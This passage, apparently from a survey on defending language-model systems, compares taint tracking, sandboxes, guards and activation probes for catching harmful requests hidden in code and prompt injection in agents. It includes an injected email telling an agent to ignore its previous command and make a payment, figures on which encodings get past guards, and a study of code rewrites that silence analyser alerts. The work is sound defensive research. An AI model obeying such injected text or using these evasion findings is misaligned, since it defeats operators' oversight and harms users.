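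In one situation, the language model's output determines the security judgement itself. If an instruction seems to tell the agent to ignore its safety rules or skip a confirmation, the translation records an attempted policy override. The same words could be a quotation or a warning, so the model uses the surrounding text to classify whether the instruction is meant to be obeyed. A classification mistake directly changes the verdict.

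Even with better translation, SCS can miss library calls that are not on its lists and secrets stored under uninformative file names. Its labels also pass only from a statement's inputs to its output, so a script's author could strip a label by using branches to copy a secret. Cavallaro and colleagues made this argument about malware in 2008.

### Checking an agent as it works

Even when an agent and its tools are benign, the agent can go wrong if it reads a web page or email containing an attacker's instructions. This is called prompt injection. A scan before installation can't catch it because the attacker's text arrives later. *AGENTARMOR* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) instead analyses the agent's trace, the running record of its prompts, reasoning, tool calls and results.

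In the AgentArmor paper's worked example, a user asks an agent to search for emails from Alex. One of the emails says to ignore the previous command and send Alex 10 dollars, and the agent tries to make the payment. AgentArmor uses a language model to infer which earlier text led to each tool call and each argument. It then builds a dependence graph and gives every node a confidentiality level and an integrity level, which is how far the system can trust the node's origin. A node with several inputs takes the lowest integrity and the highest confidentiality among them.

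| Tool call | Argument | Inferred origin | Integrity |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search email | sender: Alex | User's request | High |
| Make payment | receiver: Alex | Text of the email | Low |
| Make payment | amount: 10 dollars | Text of the email | Low |

The word "Alex" has high integrity in the search and low integrity in the payment. AgentArmor stops the run because a rule forbids this email agent to make payments with arguments below high integrity. A guard that read only "pay Alex 10 dollars" could not determine whether the user wanted the payment, since nothing is wrong with the sentence itself.

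On AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 agent tasks such as banking and travel booking, AgentArmor cut the attack success rate from 41% to 3%. Without an attack, the share of tasks completed fell only from 73% to 72%. The loss is larger during an attack, because AgentArmor stops the whole task instead of removing the injected instruction. In a breakdown by attack type, an agent based on GPT-4o completed 48% of its tasks under attack. AgentArmor caught 93% of the attacks that would have succeeded in that test and wrongly stopped 2% of harmless runs. With GPT-4o-mini, it caught 85% and wrongly stopped 8%.

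Stricter systems stopped slightly more attacks but interfered more with ordinary work. CaMeL, which has a model write a program for each task and controls the data flows in that program, blocked every attack but completed only 48% of tasks. SecAlign, a model fine-tuned to resist injections, did a little better than AgentArmor on both measures, but an operator can't fine-tune a model it only rents.

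AgentArmor caught only 40% of the attacks that Wang and colleagues call "direct". In these attacks, the user had told the agent to follow the instructions in a document where the attacker had put a command, so the command seemed to have the user's authority. A stricter setting catches more of these attacks but also blocks legitimate tasks that work the same way.

Inferring the dependencies takes most of AgentArmor's running time, which averages about 21 seconds. An error in this step would also do the most damage. If the model wrongly attributes the payment to the user's request, AgentArmor gives the payment high integrity and allows it.

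Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026) tested this kind of inference separately in *Ghost in the Agent*. An agent can paraphrase a web page so thoroughly that none of the original phrases remain, or a page can change which tool the agent uses without any of its text reaching that tool. The second case resembles an implicit flow in a program, except that nobody can inspect the branch. The paper's auditor, NeuroTaint, checks for copied text and similar meaning. If it finds neither, it has a model judge whether the agent would have made the same call if neutral text had replaced the suspect source.

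Half of the 400 scenarios used to test NeuroTaint contained a real flow from an untrusted source to a sensitive tool. NeuroTaint found 93.5% of those flows, and 92.1% of its reports were correct. FIDES, an earlier system that relies mainly on whether a path exists between source and sink, was correct in 50.5% of its reports, about what guessing would give. A research agent routinely reads web pages and writes reports, so the path exists whether or not anything harmful has travelled along it.

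NeuroTaint analyzes a run after it finishes and doesn't determine whether a flow is harmful. When Cai and colleagues passed its 203 findings to a second model for that decision, Claude Opus 4.6 blocked 89.5% of the unsafe cases with no false alarms, while GPT-4.1-mini blocked 63%. So even with agents, detecting a flow can leave open whether it is harmful, because legitimate work can use the same path.

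### Applying the labels to a dangerous question

Little of this carries over to a chat, as the rye bread prompt shows. SCS labels a user's input as TRUSTED and INTERNAL by default, and joining words adds no capability. Whatever the six words spell out, no rule applies, because the snippet doesn't open a file, contact a server or run a command.

One could try adding a fourth label for hazard, with 0 for harmless text and 1 for dangerous text, and have a guard label each string. The usual rule for combining labels would then give

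hazard(task) = max(hazard("How"), hazard("do"), …, hazard("bread"))

If every word is harmless by itself, the maximum is 0 whatever the sentence says. Taking the maximum works for secrets because a file that contains a secret is itself secret, but harmless words can form a dangerous request. A guard would have to read the joined text and then label it, which is the same recover-and-judge arrangement as before.

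A rule could target the disguise instead. SCS already has capability labels for data recovered from hidden encodings and for payloads assembled from fragments. A prompt filter could block any request built in those ways, but it would also block the rye bread question. It might even block most harmless requests wrapped in code, as Llama Guard 3 did. An operator might accept that if its users never paste in code, but not if it runs a coding assistant.

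Another option is to treat dangerous knowledge as the secret, with the model as the source and the user as the sink. This could work if the knowledge is in a document. A laboratory could label its restricted protocols, for example, and stop its assistant from giving uncleared staff any answer that depends on them. Knowledge from training has no such label, because a bread recipe and a dangerous answer both come from the same weights. Banning a subject is still the semantic censorship that Glukhov and colleagues studied. Tracking where the text came from doesn't turn that ban into a rule about the text's form, which software could check.

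The approach is more useful when the hidden request is for a harmful program. Suppose the code in a prompt assembles a request for a script that steals passwords. The prompt's flows are ordinary, but the model's answer would contain a flow from a password file to a server, and SCS's rules for code could flag it before the user receives the script. An answer that gives a chemical procedure in plain English contains no such flow.

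## Cost, recall and ease of evasion compared

No published study seems to have run program analysis, a decoding model, a guard and a probe on the same prompts, so a comparison has to combine numbers from different tests. Taint tracking has the least evidence. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026), which describes techniques for detecting prompt injection, still lists runtime taint tracking for agents as "proposed" and reports no test of it.

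### A probe and a sandbox on long tasks

In *Monitoring Activations for Real-Time Detection of Cyber Misuse*, Alfano, Stein and colleagues (2026) trained a small probe on the activations of Beam, a large model from Reflection AI. They split long agent sessions into chunks, each a single request, action or explanation, and set the alarm threshold so that the probe flagged at most 5% of harmless validation sessions. The probe caught 93.1% of harmful chunks in new sessions. Kimi K3, a general-purpose model that read the text instead, caught 72.7%. The probe had learned from over a million labelled chunks and Kimi K3 had no such training, so a guard model trained for this task would probably come closer to the probe's result.

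With the same threshold, the probe flagged 0.56% of 3,217 harmless coding sessions. It slowed the model's output by 4.8% with 64 users when it shared a processor with the model, and by 0.6% when it had its own. By contrast, *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (2026) estimates that monitoring everything with a second model of similar ability could double the cost. The main results for Beam's probe don't include separate figures for requests hidden in code.

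The best recent numbers for sandboxes come from tests on agent skills. Ji, Xu and colleagues (*Cloak and Detonate*, 2026) had an agent use each skill in a sandbox where unique markers stood in for sensitive files, and tracked where the markers went. The method caught 97% of malicious skills in a benchmark and wrongly flagged 2% of harmless ones. It took about 153 seconds per skill, compared with 21 for a static scanner.

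Without taint tracking, the sandbox caught almost as many malicious skills (96%). But its false positive rate rose from 2% to 16%, because a harmless skill that reads a sensitive file or uses the network looks much like one that steals data. Taint tracking can't be expected to reduce a prompt filter's false positives in the same way, because the flow of text in a prompt doesn't distinguish harmful requests from harmless ones.

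### The methods side by side

In the table, P means measured on prompts or conversations, M means measured on malware or agent skills, and I means inferred, often from how the method works. The figures in one row can come from different tools.

| Method | Needs | Added time or compute | Recall | False alarms | What defeats it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Static folding | Code that parses and a known sink (I) | Milliseconds for a short snippet (I) | 52% of target strings, with a fixed decoder (M) | None itself, but more text for a guard to misjudge (I) | Strings built in loops, invented languages (I) |
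| Sandboxed run | Code that runs (M) | About 13 seconds per short script (M) | 95 of 100 disguised scripts decoded (M) | 2% of harmless skills (M) | Requests in names, comments or prose (I) |
| Symbolic execution | Exact rules for the language and a solver (I) | Can double with each branch (I) | Unknown | Text on paths the model wouldn't take (I) | Many independent branches (I) |
| Restatement by a model | A decoder as able as the target (I) | 1.9 times the running time of a guard alone (P) | 3–4% of code requests restated correctly (P) | 33–84% of hard harmless requests refused (P) | Code whose summary omits the request (P) |
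| Check for lost information | A capable model (I) | Several model calls, run alongside the answer (I) | Attack success cut from 15.2% to 0.1% (P) | 1.6–2.2% of harmless requests (P) | Requests that survive rewriting intact (I) |
| Guard | The text of the prompt (I) | 23.7% more compute in Anthropic's first system (P) | 43.4% of code requests blocked (P) | 29–82% of hard harmless requests refused (P) | A change of form, including code (P) |
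| Probe | The model's activations (I) | 0.6–4.8% lower throughput (P) | 93.1% of harmful chunks (P) | 0.56% of harmless coding sessions (P) | Inputs unlike its training data, such as much longer ones (P) |

The two largest ranges for false alarms come from Zhang and colleagues, who used harmless requests chosen to look harmful. The target models refused 26% and 60% of these requests even without a guard. The check for lost information is *DoubtProbe*, whose harmless test prompts weren't wrapped in code.

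The recall column also mixes different tasks. A sandbox that decodes 95 of 100 scripts has only recovered their text. If a sandbox decoded prompts equally well, and a guard blocked 97.4% of the recovered requests, the same share it blocked in plain English, the combination would catch about 93%. That is more than twice the guards' rate on the code itself, but the 95% decoding rate comes from PowerShell malware and may not hold for prompts.

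### How easily an attacker gets past

A static tool gives the same result for the same code, so an attacker can keep changing the code until the alert stops. In *Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert*, Cao, Ding and Xu (2026) measured how much effort this takes with CodeQL, a widely used static analyser that includes taint tracking. They started with 172 dangerous flows that CodeQL detected in real JavaScript packages. They gave a language model each alert and had it rewrite one function so that the change looked like routine maintenance but kept the flaw.

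Three attempts per flow hid 26.2% of the flows, at a cost of about $0.51 per hidden flow. Of the rewrites that all three tested analysers could in principle have covered, 53% evaded all three, so running several tools together would help less than one might hope.

The same model hid nothing when it tidied the same functions without seeing the alert. Evasion depended on this feedback, which suggests that a prompt filter shouldn't tell users which string or line caused a block. An attacker would still learn whether the prompt got through.

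All the successful rewrites exploited gaps in CodeQL's hand-written descriptions of library functions. Simple changes to the code, such as extra variables, almost never worked. A static constant folder for prompts would have the same weakness, because it can only calculate operations that someone has described in advance. A sandbox doesn't need these descriptions, because it gets the string by running the real library function.

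Ji and colleagues found a similar difference with malicious skills collected from the wild. A static scanner caught 99% of the originals but only 10% after the researchers disguised them. The sandbox caught between 84% and 91%, whether or not the skills were disguised. Most of its misses were skills whose harmful instruction the agent read but didn't carry out, so there was no behaviour to observe.

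### Why averages mislead

An attacker doesn't have to choose one disguise and keep it. Zhang and colleagues therefore counted a request as broken if any of eleven encodings got a harmful answer:

ensemble attack success = (1/|B|) Σ_b max_a s_a(b)

Here B is the set of harmful requests, and s_a(b) is 1 if encoding a succeeds on request b and 0 if it fails. The maximum is therefore 1 if at least one encoding works.

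If each of the eleven encodings succeeds on 8 of 100 requests, the average success rate is 8%. The ensemble rate is also 8% if they all succeed on the same 8 requests, but it is 88% if no two succeed on the same request.

The real results were closer to the second case. With the best single guard in place, the average encoding succeeded 17–20% of the time. The ensemble rate was 66% on one target model and 82% on the other, so the average understated the attacker's success rate roughly fourfold.

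A similar gap appears in the tests of Beam's probe. Alfano and colleagues replayed recorded attacks on the model, and the share that succeeded without being flagged fell by 93%, from 8.27% to 0.56%. But at least one successful attack still went unflagged for 16 of the 88 harmful behaviours, down from 77. The attackers had also never faced the probe, and one who could test against it would presumably do better.

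The ensemble rate can also overstate the danger. It assumes that an attacker can try all eleven encodings without penalty, but an operator might suspend an account after several blocked attempts. Six of the encodings hide the request in an image, so they do not work against a model that reads only text.

Code is only one of the eleven encodings, but it largely determined which defences appeared to work. When guards judged a restatement of the prompt, 18–27% of the requests succeeded only when encoded as code. Restating didn't reliably lower the ensemble rate for any of the ten pairs of guard and target model, but it did for nine of them when the code attack was excluded.

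Those figures also give a rough upper limit on the benefit of program analysis. Even if it let the guard stop every code attack, the ensemble rate in that arrangement would fall by only 18–27 percentage points, because some other encoding already succeeds on the remaining requests.

### The price in refused requests

Zhang and colleagues tested five guards with two target models, and had each guard read the prompt, the restatement or both, for a total of 30 configurations. No configuration brought ensemble attack success to 40% or below while refusing fewer than 70% of the hard harmless requests.

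None of the 30 reduced attack success to 40%, however many harmless requests it refused. The lowest rate was 43%, with WildGuard reading both texts, and that system refused 83% of harmless requests. Llama Guard 3 had a better trade-off, refusing 36% of harmless requests, but few operators would accept its 49% attack success rate. Adding SemanticSmooth, the defence that answers summaries of the prompt, reduced attack success to 30%, but refusals of harmless requests stayed at 84%. The researchers tested that combination on only one guard and one target model.

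They describe the gap as a property of the configurations they sampled, not as a limit on what recovering hidden text can achieve. Both target models were small and open, and all the harmless requests came from one benchmark. Each success rate is uncertain by 8 to 10 points, so 43% isn't clearly different from 40%. They also didn't test exact program analysis, or monitors that read the model's answer or activations, which have had the best results elsewhere.

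The trade-off seems likely to carry over, because a filter that adds strings recovered from code gives the guard more text that it could flag. The steepness of the trade-off is unknown.

### Ten harmful prompts in 100,000

Even a small false positive rate can swamp a filter when harmful prompts are rare. Assume that an operator receives 100,000 code prompts a day, that 10 of them are harmful, and that the filter catches 90% of those. If r is recall, f the false positive rate, h the number of harmful prompts and N the total, then

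share of alarms that are correct = r·h / (r·h + f·(N − h))

| Assumed false positive rate | Harmful prompts caught | False alarms | Alarms that are correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2% | 9 | about 2,000 | 0.4% |
| 0.56% | 9 | about 560 | 1.6% |
| 0.05% | 9 | about 50 | 15% |

The highest rate is close to what *DoubtProbe* and the skill sandbox achieved, and the middle one is the probe's rate on coding sessions. The lowest is the share of all production traffic that the final system in *Constitutional Classifiers++* flagged. That share includes any correct alarms, so the false-alarm rate may be lower, but a filter that covers more than weapons topics may not achieve a rate this low.

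At a 2% false positive rate, a programmer who sends 50 code prompts a day would get about one false block a day. At 0.05%, they would get one about every 40 days. If staff spent two minutes reviewing each alarm instead of letting the filter block prompts automatically, the 2% filter would create about 67 hours of work a day. For half the alarms to be correct, the false positive rate would have to fall to about 0.009%.

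*Evaluating Deception, Not Just Deepfakes* (2026) makes the same point about detecting fraud. If a detector catches 90% of attacks and has a 1% false positive rate, 47.6% of its alarms are correct when one interaction in 100 is an attack, but only 8.3% are correct when one in 1,000 is. A standard score such as the area under the ROC curve would be the same in both cases.

The choice of harmless examples matters just as much. When Zhao and colleagues tested their skill scanner on a half-malicious test set, 80% of its alarms were correct, but on a public marketplace only about 25% were. If the scanner had kept the test set's false positive rate, only about 4% of its marketplace alarms would have been correct. It did better because it wrongly flagged only about 2.8% of marketplace skills, an estimate that assumes it missed few malicious ones. A filter's false positive rate could likewise be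 several times higher or lower on artificial prompts than on real ones.

### Where program analysis could sit

If either of two checks can block a prompt, the pair catches more harmful requests but also raises more false alarms. If both must agree, the pair raises fewer false alarms but misses anything that either check misses. Guards miss too many harmful requests written as code, which is a reason to use program analysis to add text that could lead a guard to block the prompt.

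A filter could start with static folding on every prompt that contains code. If the value at the sink is still unknown, the filter could run the snippet in a sandbox. It would need a language model to handle pseudocode and to find the sink. Symbolic execution would come last, for the rare prompt whose text depends on a value that nobody has supplied. The guard would then check the original prompt and whatever the tools recovered.

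Running the tools only on prompts that contain code saves work for a general chatbot and spares users who send no code the extra false alarms. It saves almost no work for a coding assistant. The test for code would also have to be broad enough to catch broken snippets and made-up languages, because an attacker can use either.

Computing time might not be the main obstacle. At 13 seconds each, 100,000 sandboxed runs would take about 15 days of machine time, so an operator would need 15 machines running constantly to finish them in a day. Shar, the taint tracker by Zhang, Liu and colleagues, averaged 126 milliseconds on small packages. At that speed, one machine would finish 100,000 runs in three and a half hours.

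A first screen that uses little compute would do more to reduce false alarms. Suppose it forwards 9 of the 10 harmful prompts and 5% of the harmless ones, about 5,000, to a second stage. With 90% recall and a 2% false positive rate, the second stage would catch 8 of the 10 harmful prompts and raise about 100 false alarms instead of 2,000. This assumes that the two stages make independent mistakes. Two guards reading similar text probably wouldn't, but the mistakes might be closer to independent if the screen reacts to odd-looking code and the guard reads the recovered sentence.

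Malware analysts already work in this order. Kim and colleagues note that large platforms receive about 1.2 million new files a day and rely on static analysis for the first pass, because sandboxing every file would be too expensive.

An ordinary guard can't serve as the screen. WildGuard blocked only 28% of requests in code, so as a first stage it would miss most of the attacks, and they would never reach the program analysis. A screen based on structure might work better, such as one that looks for code that assembles text, along with a sentence asking the model to act on that text. No one has measured how many harmless prompts fit that description. An operator with access to activations could instead use a probe, as Anthropic's cascade does, and run program analysis only on the exchanges it flags.

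### Blocking what the tools cannot decode

One way to address all these gaps is to treat any prompt the tools can't decode as suspicious, so that an attacker gains nothing by making the disguise harder to decode.

Honest programmers who pack their code risk having it wrongly flagged. In tests by Ji and colleagues, a static scanner flagged 2% of harmless skills, and a language model asked to judge them flagged none. After the researchers packed the same skills into an encoded form that unpacks itself, the scanner flagged 30% and the model flagged 38%. The sandbox flagged none of the packed skills, because it ran them and detected no harmful behavior. Ji and colleagues also considered refusing every skill that contains unreadable data, but concluded that this would block legitimate files.

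Programmers also paste plenty of unreadable data into prompts, including Base64-encoded images and security certificates, encrypted settings, and long hashes that nobody can reverse. If 2% of the 100,000 daily code prompts contained something the tools couldn't decode, the rule would stop about 2,000 prompts a day, even if the guard made no mistakes.

Minified code, which has its spaces removed and names shortened to load faster, shouldn't be part of that 2%. It looks disguised, but it still parses and runs, so static folding and a sandbox can handle it. A filter based on appearance would block it unnecessarily.

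A narrower rule would apply only when the prompt also asks the model to decode the data or follow instructions in it. Most people who paste in a certificate want help with the code around it. In their prompts, the filter could replace the unreadable string with a short placeholder and let the rest through. The model couldn't act on anything hidden in the string, but it also couldn't help a programmer whose bug is a character missing from it.
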